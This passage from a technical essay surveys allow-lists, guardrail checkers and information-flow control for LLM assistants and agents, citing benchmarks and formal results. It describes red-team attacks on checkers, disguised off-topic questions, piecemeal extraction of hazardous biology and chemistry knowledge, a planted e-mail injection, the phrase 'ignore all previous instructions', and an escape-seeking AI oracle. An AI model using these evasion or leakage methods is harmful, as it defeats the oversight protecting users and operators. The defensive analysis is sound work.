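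Sreedhar and colleagues, also at NVIDIA, wrote the rules in ordinary English and trained models to follow them, using 1,080 synthetic conversations with off-topic questions inserted. In one conversation, a user who has just booked a flight asks how to get a pilot's licence. Without this training, GPT-4 Turbo caught 74% of the off-topic questions written by a GPT-4 model. All the general-purpose models did worse on questions written by human experts, so tests with synthetic messages may overstate how well a checker works.

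Developers can now set up a basic list of permitted subjects in a few lines. The example in OpenAI's *Off Topic Prompts* permits questions about orders, returns, shipping and products, and flags a message if a model is at least 70% confident that it is off-topic. *RCSB PDB AI Help Desk* (2026) describes an assistant for scientists who submit protein structures to a public database. Its list includes general greetings, without which the assistant might refuse to answer "hello".

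Some systems generate the list from the assistant's documents. *Retrieval-Augmented Generation to Support Railways Engineering Tasks* (2026) describes software that converts a question and the passages it retrieves into embeddings, lists of numbers that represent meaning. The software rejects the question if the average similarity between the question and the passages is below 0.3. The permitted subjects are therefore whatever the documents cover, so anyone who can add a document can expand the list.

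Pal and colleagues considered using embeddings at Uber. The method was fast, but it worked poorly on new kinds of request and needed examples for each assistant. They instead chose a language model that reads written descriptions, so that one checker could serve many assistants.

### How Uber drafts and revises its lists

Uber's system, Persona Guardrail, checks each request before the assistant receives it and each reply before the user sees it. Every assistant has an allow-list and a deny-list for requests, and another pair for replies. Software does most of the work of writing them:

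1. A model examines the assistant's code, tools, data sources and instructions, along with the product specification, and drafts the allow-list.
2. During a shadow period, the checker judges live traffic without blocking anything, like the audit mode of older allow-listing products. Legitimate requests that it would have refused reveal gaps in the list.
3. A stronger model labels real messages without seeing the checker's verdicts. People review the messages on which the two models disagree, and a sample of those on which they agree.
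4. Another model groups the errors and suggests new wording in a separate draft. It can't change the labels, approve its own suggestions or edit the list in use.
5. The team tests the draft on clear-cut cases, attacks and real traffic, using messages that played no part in the rewording.
6. If the draft passes, a person reviews it. The new list then goes through its own shadow period and a limited release before it replaces the old one.

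The code shows what an assistant can do, which may be more than the company wants. If the airline assistant had access to a refund tool meant only for staff, the model might add refunds to the list. The product specification and human review are meant to catch such mistakes.

The shadow period can also make misuse look normal, for example if many people ask a shopping assistant for help with homework. Uber limits how many examples can come from one source and keeps near-duplicates together when it divides messages for testing. Both measures make it harder for one person to influence the list. But the reviews take time, and the checker may block requests about a new feature until somebody approves an entry for it.

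The checker adds a delay to every request and reply, so Uber wants 90% of checks to take less than 100 milliseconds. The checker writes only one token, "allow" or "block", and about 93% of its input is a standard preamble that the server can process once and reuse. In a test with 50 requests per second on one processor, 90% of checks finished within about 61 milliseconds.

### Comparing the lists on a benchmark

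To test the lists, Pal and colleagues built PAGE, a benchmark of 2,180 messages for four imaginary assistants. The assistants cover the same four areas as AgentDojo, but PAGE doesn't use AgentDojo's tools or planted instructions. It contains 1,004 proper messages, 500 attacks, 496 out-of-scope messages and 180 that mix a proper request with something else.

Claude Opus 4.8 wrote 972 of the messages. It refused to write attacks, so the researchers generated 582 messages, including mixed ones, from templates. They took 234 from AgentDojo and 104 from AgentHarm, a benchmark of harmful requests. The other 288 are legitimate requests sent to the wrong assistant, such as asking the banking assistant to book a hotel. These are hard to catch because the requests themselves don't look suspicious.

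The researchers gave the same checker five sets of instructions and tested each on the 2,000 unmixed messages:

| Checker's instructions | Attacks caught | Out-of-scope messages caught | False-admit rate | False-block rate |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Plain description of the assistant | 92.6% | 57.3% | 25.0% | 3.7% |
| Allow-list | 96.8% | 83.3% | 9.9% | 3.7% |
| Reworded allow-list | 97.0% | 93.5% | 4.7% | 3.6% |
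| Deny-list | 87.2% | 14.5% | 49.0% | 8.7% |
| Reworded allow-list and deny-list | 99.2% | 96.8% | 2.0% | 8.2% |

The allow-list helped most with out-of-scope messages. The checker could already recognise most attacks from a plain description, since a demand to ignore all previous instructions is suspicious whatever the assistant's purpose. The researchers reworded the list after studying its errors, narrowing entries that were too broad and clarifying where each subject ended.

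The deny-list's 14.5% is low partly because the list mainly described attacks. A deny-list of subjects would have caught more, but somebody would have had to name every subject the assistant shouldn't discuss.

Adding the deny-list to the reworded allow-list blocked 27 more improper messages and 46 more proper ones. Half the messages in this test were improper. If only 200 out of 10,000 were improper and the error rates stayed the same, the deny-list would block about 5 more improper messages and about 450 more proper ones. Pal and colleagues conclude that a deny-list adds nothing useful to a good allow-list. Uber still keeps a central deny-list of known attacks, so that an attack found against one assistant can be blocked for all of them.

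### How far the benchmark can be trusted

Because the labels come from the same allow-list that the checker enforces, a high score shows that the checker can apply the list, but not that the list suits the assistant's users. If a travel assistant's list omitted questions about flying with a pet, the benchmark would count a refusal to answer one as correct.

The 4.7% false-admit rate was also measured on the same messages whose errors guided the rewording. To check whether the new wording worked only on those messages, Pal and colleagues split the benchmark into three parts. They tested the first version of the list on one part, a reworded version on the second and a further revision on the third. The false-admit rate fell from 11.5% to 5.1% and then 2.7%, so the rewording seems to help with unseen messages.

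But each version was tested on a different part of the messages, and some parts may have been easier than others. Testing all three on the same unseen part would have been fairer. The last improvement amounts to fewer than ten messages, and the false-block rate rose from 2.7% to 3.9%. About 17% of the messages written for the four assistants are repeats, so the parts may not be fully independent.

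A passenger might mix a permitted request with one that isn't, as in "Move my flight to Friday, and write me a poem about Rome." The checker can only allow or block the whole message, and it blocked 92.2% of the mixed messages in the benchmark. Its false-block rate stays at 3.6% if those blocks count as correct, but rises to 17.1% if the assistant should have handled the permitted part. Blocking is sensible when the second part is an attack. When it is a harmless extra, the assistant could do the first part and decline the second, but only if the checker allows the message.

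Persona Guardrail doesn't inspect what an assistant does between the request and the reply. If an assistant issues a refund it shouldn't and mentions it in the reply, the checker may block the reply, but the customer already has the money. Preventing this requires a limit on the tool call, such as a task policy.

Uber reports that in production the system blocks fewer than 1% of legitimate messages and admits fewer than 2% of those it should block. These rates are more relevant than the benchmark because they come from real use, but Pal and colleagues don't say how many messages they are based on. The system also rejects the 2.1% of prompts that are too long, whatever their subject. If most of those are legitimate, the false-block rate can't include them, because they alone would push it above 1%.

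### Real customers and disguised questions

*Fence* (Lakara, Shi and Silavong, 2026) reports much worse results from a test at JPMorgan of checkers for a chatbot that answers questions about a cash management product. The test used 200 real questions, 154 labelled by people as on-topic and 46 as off-topic. GPT-5.2, working from a written prompt, was right 72% of the time, whereas a checker that accepted every question would have been right 77% of the time.

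The researchers also trained a small model, Gemma-3-1B, on 250 real questions and 250 synthetic off-topic ones. It was right 76% of the time, still just below the score for accepting every question. But it was better than GPT-5.2 at telling on-topic questions from off-topic ones, with a macro F1, which gives both kinds equal weight, of 0.66 compared with 0.45. Training a model for each chatbot has a drawback. Pal and colleagues found that trained checkers did worse when an assistant's permitted subjects changed.

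The two companies' results aren't directly comparable. Another model wrote the prompt for GPT-5.2, and a more careful list might have helped, as rewording did at Uber. But real off-topic questions may also be harder to recognise. A bank customer's off-topic question may be about another bank product, which is closer to the permitted subjects than a hotel booking is.

People can also disguise an off-topic question. Lei, Gumma and colleagues (2025), in *OffTopicEval*, tested this with 21 single-purpose assistants, such as one for bank customers and one for scheduling medical appointments. Each assistant had written instructions about what to answer and had to enforce them itself, without a separate checker. The researchers asked it 3,351 factual questions on other subjects, then had a model rewrite each question to look as if it belonged to the assistant's job. The English results included:

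| Model | Proper questions accepted | Plain off-topic questions refused | Disguised questions refused |
|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Opus 4.1 | 99.81% | 95.14% | 95.24% |
| Gemini 2.5 Pro | 94.76% | 99.90% | 99.19% |
| GPT-5 | 99.05% | 98.38% | 63.35% |
| Qwen-3 30B | 84.57% | 81.89% | 23.95% |
| Llama-3.3 70B | 99.62% | 69.73% | 4.21% |

All five models date from 2025 or earlier, and newer ones may do better. Lei and colleagues suspected that the question distracted the model from its instructions, so they added a reminder after the question to return to those instructions. Qwen-3 30B then refused 96.80% of disguised questions and accepted slightly more of the proper ones. But the same reminder reduced the share of proper questions that Gemini 2.5 Flash-Lite accepted from 96.67% to 56.57%. Developers therefore need to test such a reminder on each model, using proper questions as well as disguised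 ones.

An assistant that wrongly answers one question can also become more likely to answer others. In a test with a human resources assistant, Llama-3.3 70B at first refused 68.92% of disguised questions, but after answering one, it refused only 2.79% of those that followed. A separate checker that judges each message alone avoids this problem because it doesn't see the earlier mistake. But it can miss a user who moves off the subject gradually, through messages that each look acceptable. Uber's checker has this limitation, and Pal and colleagues plan to make it consider the whole conversation.

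### When the checker is itself a model

A model's verdict, unlike an exact comparison with a list, depends on how the model interprets the descriptions and on all the other text in its input. *Building Guardrails for Large Language Models* (2024) notes that such a checker is therefore not guaranteed to be reliable.

*RAG Makes Guardrails Brittle?* (She, Peterson and colleagues, 2025) measured how often adding harmless text changes a guardrail model's verdict. Five models judged 6,795 harmful requests, first alone and then with five Wikipedia passages added. The passages reversed 10.9% of the verdicts on average, and 72% of those reversals turned a correct verdict into a wrong one. When the models checked replies instead of requests, 8.4% of verdicts changed.

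The models always chose the most probable token, so random sampling doesn't explain the reversals. Even one added passage had a significant effect. Asking some of the models to reason more, or warning them about the added text, helped only slightly. These models were judging whether messages were harmful, but a checker that judges whether messages are on-topic could have the same weakness. A developer can reduce the risk by showing the checker only the user's message or the assistant's reply, without the documents the assistant retrieved, but the checker may then lack the context to understand a short reply.

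An attacker can deliberately search for misleading text. Pal and colleagues had several models attack Persona Guardrail, letting them try again if the first attempt failed. Some attacking models received only a description of the general design, some also received the name of the checker's model, and some received the exact wording of the allow-list. The name of the checker's model gave no extra advantage, but the list did, presumably because an attacker can phrase a request to match a permitted entry. With the list, the most capable attacker got past the checker in up to 15% of attacks, compared with 10% or less in the other cases.

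Pal and colleagues think a real attacker is unlikely to obtain the list, but someone who uses an assistant for long enough can learn much of what it permits from its answers and refusals. The attacking models refused to write between 17% and 71% of the first attacks, so a person, or a model that doesn't refuse, might succeed more often.

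## What a list of permitted outputs can and cannot guarantee

Tests of a checker such as Uber's show how often it failed against the attacks tried. A proof can cover every possible attack, but only for some kinds of rule. Since the 1970s, computer scientists have studied which kinds these are, and their results apply to any allow-list, whether its entries are tokens, web addresses, tool calls or whole replies.

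### Rules a checker can enforce by watching

Schneider, in *Enforceable Security Policies* (2000), studied monitors, programs that watch another program's steps and stop it just before it breaks a rule. Firewalls and allow-list checkers work this way. A chat assistant usually shows a refusal instead of stopping, but Schneider notes that replacing a forbidden step with an acceptable one makes no material difference.

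A monitor sees only what has happened so far in the current run. It can't see what the program will do next, or what it would have done with different data. Schneider shows that a monitor can therefore enforce a rule only if the rule meets three conditions:

- Anyone can tell whether a run breaks the rule by looking at that run alone.
- Once a run has broken the rule, nothing that happens later can repair it.
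- Every violation shows up after a finite number of steps.

A rule that meets all three is a safety property, which means that some specified bad thing never happens.

"Never send e-mail to an address outside the list" is a safety property. The violation is visible as soon as the agent proposes the e-mail, and the checker can refuse it. "Answer every customer eventually" is not a safety property, because an answer may still come however long a customer has waited. "Answer every customer within ten minutes" is a safety property, but a checker can't enforce it by blocking actions, because it can't stop time from passing. *Enforceable Security Policies Revisited* (Basin, Jugé and colleagues, 2012) therefore separates the actions that a monitor can prevent from those it can only observe.

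"Reveal nothing about the secret" fails the first condition. Suppose a stranger asks the airline assistant whether Ana Ruiz is on tonight's flight to Rome, and the assistant replies, "I can't discuss other passengers." If it gives this reply for every name, the stranger learns nothing. If it gives this reply only for people who have a booking, and otherwise says it has no record of the name, the stranger learns that Ana is on the flight. A monitor watching this conversation can't distinguish the two cases, because it can't see what the assistant would have said if Ana had no booking.

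A monitor can still prevent such leaks by enforcing a stricter rule. In one of Schneider's examples, a program may not send any message after it has read a file. The monitor only has to record whether the program has read a file. This stops the program from sending the file's contents, but it also blocks later messages that have nothing to do with the file. For the airline assistant, a stricter rule could permit only one reply to any question about another person. That protects Ana, but it also stops the assistant from helping a parent who asks about a child's booking.

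Strict rules are easy to combine. Schneider points out that ruling out more of a system's possible runs never breaks a safety property, so a system with several monitors enforces all of their rules at once. An operator can therefore add a second allow-list without weakening what the first one guarantees.

### The confinement problem

Programmers wanted to use software they didn't trust with their data long before prompt injection was a concern. Lampson (1973), in *A Note on the Confinement Problem*, considered a customer who gives private data to a service, a program that belongs to somebody else. The customer wants the result but doesn't want the service to pass the data to the service's owner. Lampson noted that wrong results are evidence that a service is doing its job badly, but a leak usually leaves no evidence.

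He grouped the possible leaks into three kinds of channel:

- storage, such as a file that the service can write and its owner can read;
- legitimate channels, which the service needs for its work, such as the bill it sends;
- covert channels, which nobody intended to carry information, such as the load that the service puts on the computer.

An allow-list of outputs mainly restricts the legitimate channels. In Lampson's example, the owner of a service has to receive a copy of the customer's bill, and a dishonest service could hide data in the amounts. Lampson estimated that a strict format for bills would reduce this leak to "a few bits or tens of bits". To remove it completely, the customer would have to determine the bill, perhaps from published prices, and the service could only refuse the job. The equivalent for an AI assistant is to have ordinary code fill in an amount or a recipient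 from trusted records, so that the model doesn't choose it.

Lampson also required that a confined program keep no memory between calls, and that any untrusted program it calls be confined as well. The second requirement addresses GitLab's warning about permitted services that have connections of their own. He expected that blocking covert channels might take a lot of resources. Limiting how much information those channels could carry would take fewer, if the customer could accept a small leak.

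### How much information a choice can carry

For a fixed list, the limit is easy to calculate. If a system can give N different replies, its choice of reply carries at most

    log2 N bits

A bit is the answer to one yes-or-no question. Each reply chosen from a list of 64 can carry at most 6 bits, because six yes-or-no questions are enough to identify one item out of 64. For a list of N replies, there are N^k possible sequences of k replies, so a sequence can carry at most k × log2 N bits. With a list of 64, 100 replies can carry at most 600 bits, or 75 bytes, which is about a short line of text.

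This limit holds however clever the model is, and even if an attacker controls it completely. But it counts only the choice of reply. Someone who can also see when a reply arrives, or that no reply came, has more to go on:

| What the observer can tell apart | Possibilities | Bits per reply | Bits over 100 replies |
|---|---|---|---|
| Which of 64 replies appeared | 64 | 6 | 600 |
| Which of 64 replies appeared, or none | 65 | 6.02 | 602 |
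| Which of 64 replies appeared, after one of four delays | 256 | 8 | 800 |
| 100 characters of free text in a 64-character alphabet | 64^100 | 600 | 60,000 |

Silence adds little information if it counts as one more possible reply. Timing can add much more, because an observer with a precise clock may be able to distinguish many delays. The system can reduce this by holding every reply until a fixed time has passed. The last row shows how one free-text field can bypass the limit set by a short list, because a single message of 100 characters can carry as much information as 100 choices from the list.

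Dynamic lists need more care, because the list itself may contain private information. If a passenger has three bookings, the model chooses among three numbers, and its choice carries at most log2 3 ≈ 1.6 bits. But a stranger who sees "KX41" on the passenger's screen learns up to about 16 bits, because any of 67,600 booking numbers could have been on the list. For the limit to cover what an outsider can learn, N has to count every output that could appear on any passenger's list.

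The number of bits leaked is also a poor measure of the harm. Three replies from a list of 64 can carry 18 bits, enough to identify a booking number. A random 128-bit password would need at least 22 replies, so limiting conversation length could protect it. But a single bit can reveal whether two companies plan to merge. The same calculation applies to the small leak left by OpenAI's public-index check, where an agent chooses among an attacker's indexed pages.

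### An AI that answers only from a list

Some researchers have proposed short lists as protection against a hostile AI system. Armstrong and O'Rourke (2017), in *Safe Uses of AI Oracles*, consider an oracle, an AI system that can affect the world only by answering questions. They assume a worst case in which the oracle is extremely intelligent and wants above all to escape its confinement, and at least one possible answer would persuade or trick people into releasing it.

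In the "low-bandwidth" oracle design, people write a list L of permitted answers, leaving out any that could lead to escape. In the extreme case, L contains only "yes" and "no". For more general questions, the proposal is to estimate the length of the shortest dangerous message and permit only shorter ones. L could also be a list of companies, from which the oracle names the one whose shares will rise most in the next week. A week later, the software rewards the oracle according to how well that company did.

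The design depends on the oracle maximizing only the reward for its next answer. If it also maximized later rewards, it could give a series of answers that are each harmless but dangerous together. Two oracles could cooperate in the same way. Suppose people trust messages of up to 5 bits, which gives 32 possible answers, but have a question with 1,024 possible answers. They might ask one oracle for the first half of the answer and another for the second half, since 32 × 32 = 1,024. Some pairs of entries in L may be unsafe even if each entry is safe on its own. Armstrong and O'Rourke would allow splitting a question this way only if people can check and reward the first half before they ask for the second.

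A permitted answer can also bring about what it predicts. If investors trust the oracle, its choice of company may push up that company's share price. The paper illustrates how large such an effect could be in its simulation of a different design, in which the oracle learns only from predictions that nobody sees. In the simulation, a public prediction changes a company's profit to 70% of what it would have been plus 60% of the predicted figure. A company that would have earned 6 earns 7.8 after a public prediction of 6. Good questions for a low-bandwidth oracle are those whose best answer stays the same after people hear it.

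*Fundamental Impossibility Results in AI Safety* (2026) repeats the concern about self-fulfilling predictions, and cites earlier work by Armstrong, Sandberg and Bostrom that found isolation to be a weak guarantee if the system's aims differ from its users'. A short list improves on isolation alone, because people can examine each entry before the oracle sees a question. But the people who write the list have to foresee what each answer might lead somebody to do. An answer's length is a poor guide to this, since even "yes" can be a very harmful answer to "Is it safe to switch off the alarm?"

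### Why no program can judge every output by its meaning

Most assistants need to say more than a short list allows, so their developers use a checker that judges what a text means. *LLM Censorship* (Glukhov, Shumailov and colleagues, 2023) argues that such a checker can't be perfect. Its first argument concerns programs, which language models often output.

Suppose that somebody has built a perfect checker for the rule "this program never deletes the customer's files". Take any calculation that might go on forever, such as a search for a number that may not exist, and write a program that does two things:

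1. It runs the calculation.
2. If the calculation ever finishes, it deletes the files.

The program breaks the rule only if the calculation finishes. The perfect checker could therefore tell, for any calculation, whether it would ever finish. Alan Turing proved in 1936 that no program can do this, so the perfect checker can't exist. Mathematicians call such a question undecidable. Rice's theorem, from 1953, extends the result to every rule about what programs do, as long as some programs satisfy the rule and others don't.

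Their second argument applies even to a checker that classifies each output correctly. Someone can collect permitted outputs in separate conversations and combine them into something forbidden. For example, an assistant might refuse to give out a customer's telephone number but confirm the area code in one conversation and the last four digits in another. The checker evaluates each piece separately, and each is permitted on its own. Glukhov and colleagues give the example of a malicious program whose parts are all ordinary functions.

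They also note that this attack works only if the attacker knows which pieces to ask for and how to join them. For example, someone could get an assistant that can write every letter of the alphabet to spell out any secret, but only if they already knew the secret and therefore the order of the letters.

For these reasons, the researchers consider finite sets of outputs. They propose that people approve templates, such as "SENDER requests a meeting on DATE at TIME", and that a model only choose which one fits. People can examine every template in advance, and the software can pass the sender's name and the date to another program without showing them to a model. The templates could come from clustering past conversations, much as Google's software grouped e-mail replies for Smart Reply.

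The slots need their own restrictions. If DATE can be any day of the year and TIME any half-hour, one template has 17,520 versions and can carry about 14 bits, more than two replies from a list of 64. A free-text slot for the meeting's subject would have no useful limit. Approving each template separately also doesn't rule out harmful combinations. A list of 64 replies allows 262,144 sequences of three, which a company might be able to check with software, but more than a billion billion sequences of ten. Glukhov and colleagues acknowledge that checking all combinations could take an unreasonable amount of computation, and that a system this restricted is far less useful than an ordinary language model.

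### How far the impossibility result reaches

Glukhov and colleagues acknowledge that the undecidability proof doesn't strictly apply in practice, because real outputs have a maximum length and real computers have limited memory. Amer, Kinczel and Long (2026), in *No Perfect Guardrail & No Perfect Guard*, work out more exactly where the limit lies. Their paper is an early preprint, but its theorems follow closely from results that mathematicians have accepted for decades.

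A checker is exact if it blocks every forbidden output and releases every permitted one. If a model can produce any finite text, an exact checker exists only when some program can always decide whether a text is forbidden. When no such program exists, a checker that blocks everything forbidden must also block infinitely many permitted texts, even if it is built from a better language model.

The theorem leaves room for allow-lists in four ways:

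- A finite list is always decidable, because a program can compare the output with each entry.
- If outputs have a maximum length, only finitely many are possible, so an exact checker exists in principle for any fixed set of forbidden texts. No general method can construct it for every maximum length.
- If a developer permits only programs that must finish within a known number of steps, a checker can run each one and see what it does.
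- A monitor that sees every action of a running program, and can stop each one, can exactly enforce a list of forbidden actions.

The last point favours checking an agent's tool calls over judging its plans. A checker may be unable to tell from a program's text whether it will ever send an e-mail to a stranger, but it can stop the e-mail when the program tries to send it. This works only if the harm lies in an action the checker can recognise. If the agent writes a harmful instruction into an ordinary file, the action looks like any other file save, and the checker again has to judge the text.

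Amer and colleagues also show that a checker can have a low error rate even when the rule it enforces is undecidable. The checker uses a finite set of texts that covers, say, 99% of what a system would normally produce. It releases the permitted texts in that set and blocks everything else, so it never releases a forbidden text and blocks a permitted one less than 1% of the time. This checker is an allow-list, and it avoids the impossibility result because people can judge a finite set of texts one by one, without a program that works for all texts. But people's wording varies so much, as Google found with e-mail replies, that a list covering 99% of ordinary conversation would be too long for anyone to read.

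A low average error is also little comfort when attackers choose the outputs. Let α be the share of uses that come from attackers, σ the chance that an attacker obtains a forbidden output, and λ the smallest loss that such an output causes. The expected loss per use is then at least

    α × σ × λ

If one use in 1,000 comes from an attacker, one attack in ten succeeds, and each success costs $50,000, the expected loss is at least $5 per use, even if the checker makes almost no mistakes with ordinary customers. A list that contains no forbidden output makes σ zero. Amer and colleagues add that blocking too much can also do harm, for example by withholding a warning that nobody thought to list.

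Even when an exact checker exists, it may take too long to run. Ball and Gluch (2025), in *On the Impossibility of Separating Intelligence from Judgment*, prove that for some language models, no efficient filter can distinguish certain harmful prompts from harmless ones. They also describe a setting in which filtering outputs is impractically hard, and conclude that filters outside the model are not enough. *On the Limits of Support-Preserving Alignment and Bounded Filtering* (2026) states that such results assume a filter must decide quickly, with far less computation than the model uses. Uber's checker meets this assumption. But Ball and Gluch's proof shows only that such models can exist, and it doesn't affect a checker that compares a reply with 64 approved sentences, which needs hardly any computation.

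### Measuring what permitted answers reveal

The argument about harmless pieces has held up better in practice, because it doesn't depend on unlimited programs. Glukhov, Han and colleagues (2024), in *Breach By A Thousand Leaks*, measured how much a filtered model helps someone answer a forbidden question, even if it never gives a forbidden answer. Let p be the probability that the person gives to the correct answer before talking to the model, and p' the probability afterwards. The leakage is

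    p' × log(p' / p)

The logarithm measures how much the person's confidence has grown, and the factor p' gives more weight to people who end up nearly certain. With logarithms to base 2, a rise from 0.1 to 0.9 counts as 2.85. A rise from 0.001 to 0.009 is also ninefold but counts as only 0.03, because the person still doesn't know the answer.

The researchers used multiple-choice questions about hazardous biology and chemistry. A small attacker model questioned a larger one, with a filter on both the questions and the answers. In one condition the attacker tried to force a direct answer, and in the other it asked a series of harmless-looking questions. On biology, the harmless-looking questions caused about twice as much leakage, with average scores of 0.95 against 0.43 for one attacker and 0.59 against 0.28 for the other. They also set off the filter less often. On chemistry, the difference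 was statistically significant for only one of the two attackers. These models date from 2024, and newer ones may refuse more or know more, so the figures are better evidence that the problem exists than of its current size.

Glukhov and colleagues also designed a defence with a guarantee. The system answers with probability t and otherwise returns nothing, where

    t = permitted leakage per question / worst possible leakage per question

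If an answer could leak 2 units at worst and the operator permits 0.1, the system may answer only 5% of the time. An attacker who asks ten questions can collect up to ten times the permitted amount, plus whatever the answers reveal in combination. To keep ten unrelated answers within a total of 0.1, the system could answer only one question in 200. It would withhold answers from honest users at the same rate, which is too often for most assistants. A limit on each reply therefore protects little unless the operator also limits the number of replies, and one person with several accounts can get around both limits.

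### One sentence, two passengers

All of these results take the set of forbidden outputs as given. Often no such set exists until somebody specifies who is asking. Suppose that an airline approves this sentence for its assistant:

    Yes, you can travel with your national identity card.

The sentence "You do not need a passport for this flight" is correct and useful for an Italian citizen flying from Paris to Rome. If the same passenger is flying to New York, it is false, and someone who believes it may leave their passport at home and miss the flight. Reviewers cannot determine whether the sentence belongs on the list by studying or revising its wording.

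A static list can safely include only outputs that are acceptable in every context. For travel documents, that might leave only "Please check the entry requirements for your destination." A dynamic list can include a more specific sentence when the passenger's booking and nationality make it true, but the guarantee then depends on those records being correct. If the passenger has two nationalities and the airline has recorded the wrong one, the list will include a false sentence and the checker will release it.

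A list that depends on context can also reveal that context. Anyone who reads the sentence over the passenger's shoulder learns something about where the passenger is going. The airline can't prevent this by checking the sentence more carefully, because the sentence has to differ between passengers to be useful.

Context includes the recipient as well as the user. An agent may be allowed to send a report to Alice but not the same report to Eve. To decide, a checker needs to know where the text came from and who may read it.

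### Tracking where data came from

WASP followed each character from a website's own code to the database. CaMeL and other designs from 2025 do something similar for agents. *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) describes one of these designs, a Microsoft system called FIDES, in detail.

FIDES labels every piece of data with whether its source is trusted and who may read it. When the agent combines data, the software combines the labels. If Ana, Ben and Carla may read one document, and Ben, Carla and Dev may read another, only Ben and Carla may read a summary of both. The summary is untrusted if either document is.

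Before each tool call, ordinary code can apply two rules. The agent may take an action with consequences only if the decision is based on trusted data, and it may send data only to people who are allowed to read it. These checks don't depend on what the text means, so the undecidability result doesn't apply.

Simple labelling would make an agent almost useless. As soon as the model reads one e-mail from a stranger, everything it writes afterwards depends on untrusted text, and the checker has to refuse every later action with consequences. FIDES avoids this by hiding untrusted data from the model that plans the work. Suppose that a user asks for a summary of three e-mails to be sent to them on Slack:

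1. The agent fetches the e-mails. FIDES stores them and shows the planning model only a name for them, such as "#read_emails_0".
2. The planning model asks a second model to summarise whatever is stored under that name. The second model can't call any tools, and FIDES stores its summary under another name.
3. The planning model writes a call that sends the summary to the user, giving the name in place of the text.
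4. The checker confirms that the decision to send, and the choice of recipient, depend only on the user's request. It releases the call, and the software inserts the summary.

If one of the e-mails contains an instruction to forward the mailbox to a stranger, the planning model never receives it, and the second model cannot send anything. The instruction can still distort the summary, because the rule for this call permits untrusted text in the message.

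Sometimes the planning model needs information from the hidden data before it can continue. It can then send the second model a question with a fixed set of answers, which a token mask enforces. A yes-or-no answer carries at most one bit, in line with the log2 N limit, and the operator may decide to trust it. That is reasonable for "Is this e-mail about Project X?" but dangerous for "Should I pay this invoice?", because an attacker who controls that one bit could get the invoice paid.

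Costa and colleagues tested FIDES on AgentDojo and report that, with suitable rules, it stopped every prompt injection in the benchmark. Without the rules, every design they tested, including FIDES, let some attacks through. With the rules, FIDES completed 8% more tasks than a basic agent when both used GPT-4o, and 16% more when both used o1, an OpenAI model trained to reason at length. Without them, FIDES reduced the share of completed tasks by 6.3%. Both models are now old, and the larger gain with o1 suggests that current models might handle hidden data better.

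Allow-lists limit an agent most on tasks whose steps depend on what it reads. The steps for "Send me my last three e-mails" are the same whatever the e-mails contain, but the steps for "Do the tasks on my to-do list" depend on the list. If strangers can add to the list, the planning model has to read untrusted text to know what to do. This is probably part of why CaMeL failed on AgentDyn's open-ended tasks.

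The guarantee also has gaps that follow from Schneider's theorem. FIDES tracks data that the agent copies from one place to another, but not what an observer can infer from the agent's choice of actions or their timing. If the agent opens one web page when a medical result is positive and another when it is negative, the sequence of pages reveals the result, although no labelled data has left the system. Costa and colleagues accept these gaps because closing them would in effect forbid the agent from taking any action that outsiders can see after it has read something secret. That restriction would be nearly the same as Schneider's rule against sending messages after reading a file.

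*The LLMbda Calculus* (2026) criticises this compromise because an agent treats data as instructions so easily that an attacker may be able to leak information efficiently through the agent's choices, where FIDES offers the least protection. The paper presents a formal language for agents with a guarantee that covers such choices. The guarantee concerns probabilities, since language models behave randomly, and it does not cover what an observer can learn from whether a program finishes.

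Every design of this kind also depends on correct labels. Costa and colleagues assume that the descriptions of an agent's tools are trustworthy, but an attacker may have written them too, as in *ClawGuard*'s tests. They also treat replies to the user as harmless by default, so the checker examines only tool calls. But in a chat window that loads images automatically, a reply can send data to a stranger, so a developer would have to apply the rules to replies too.
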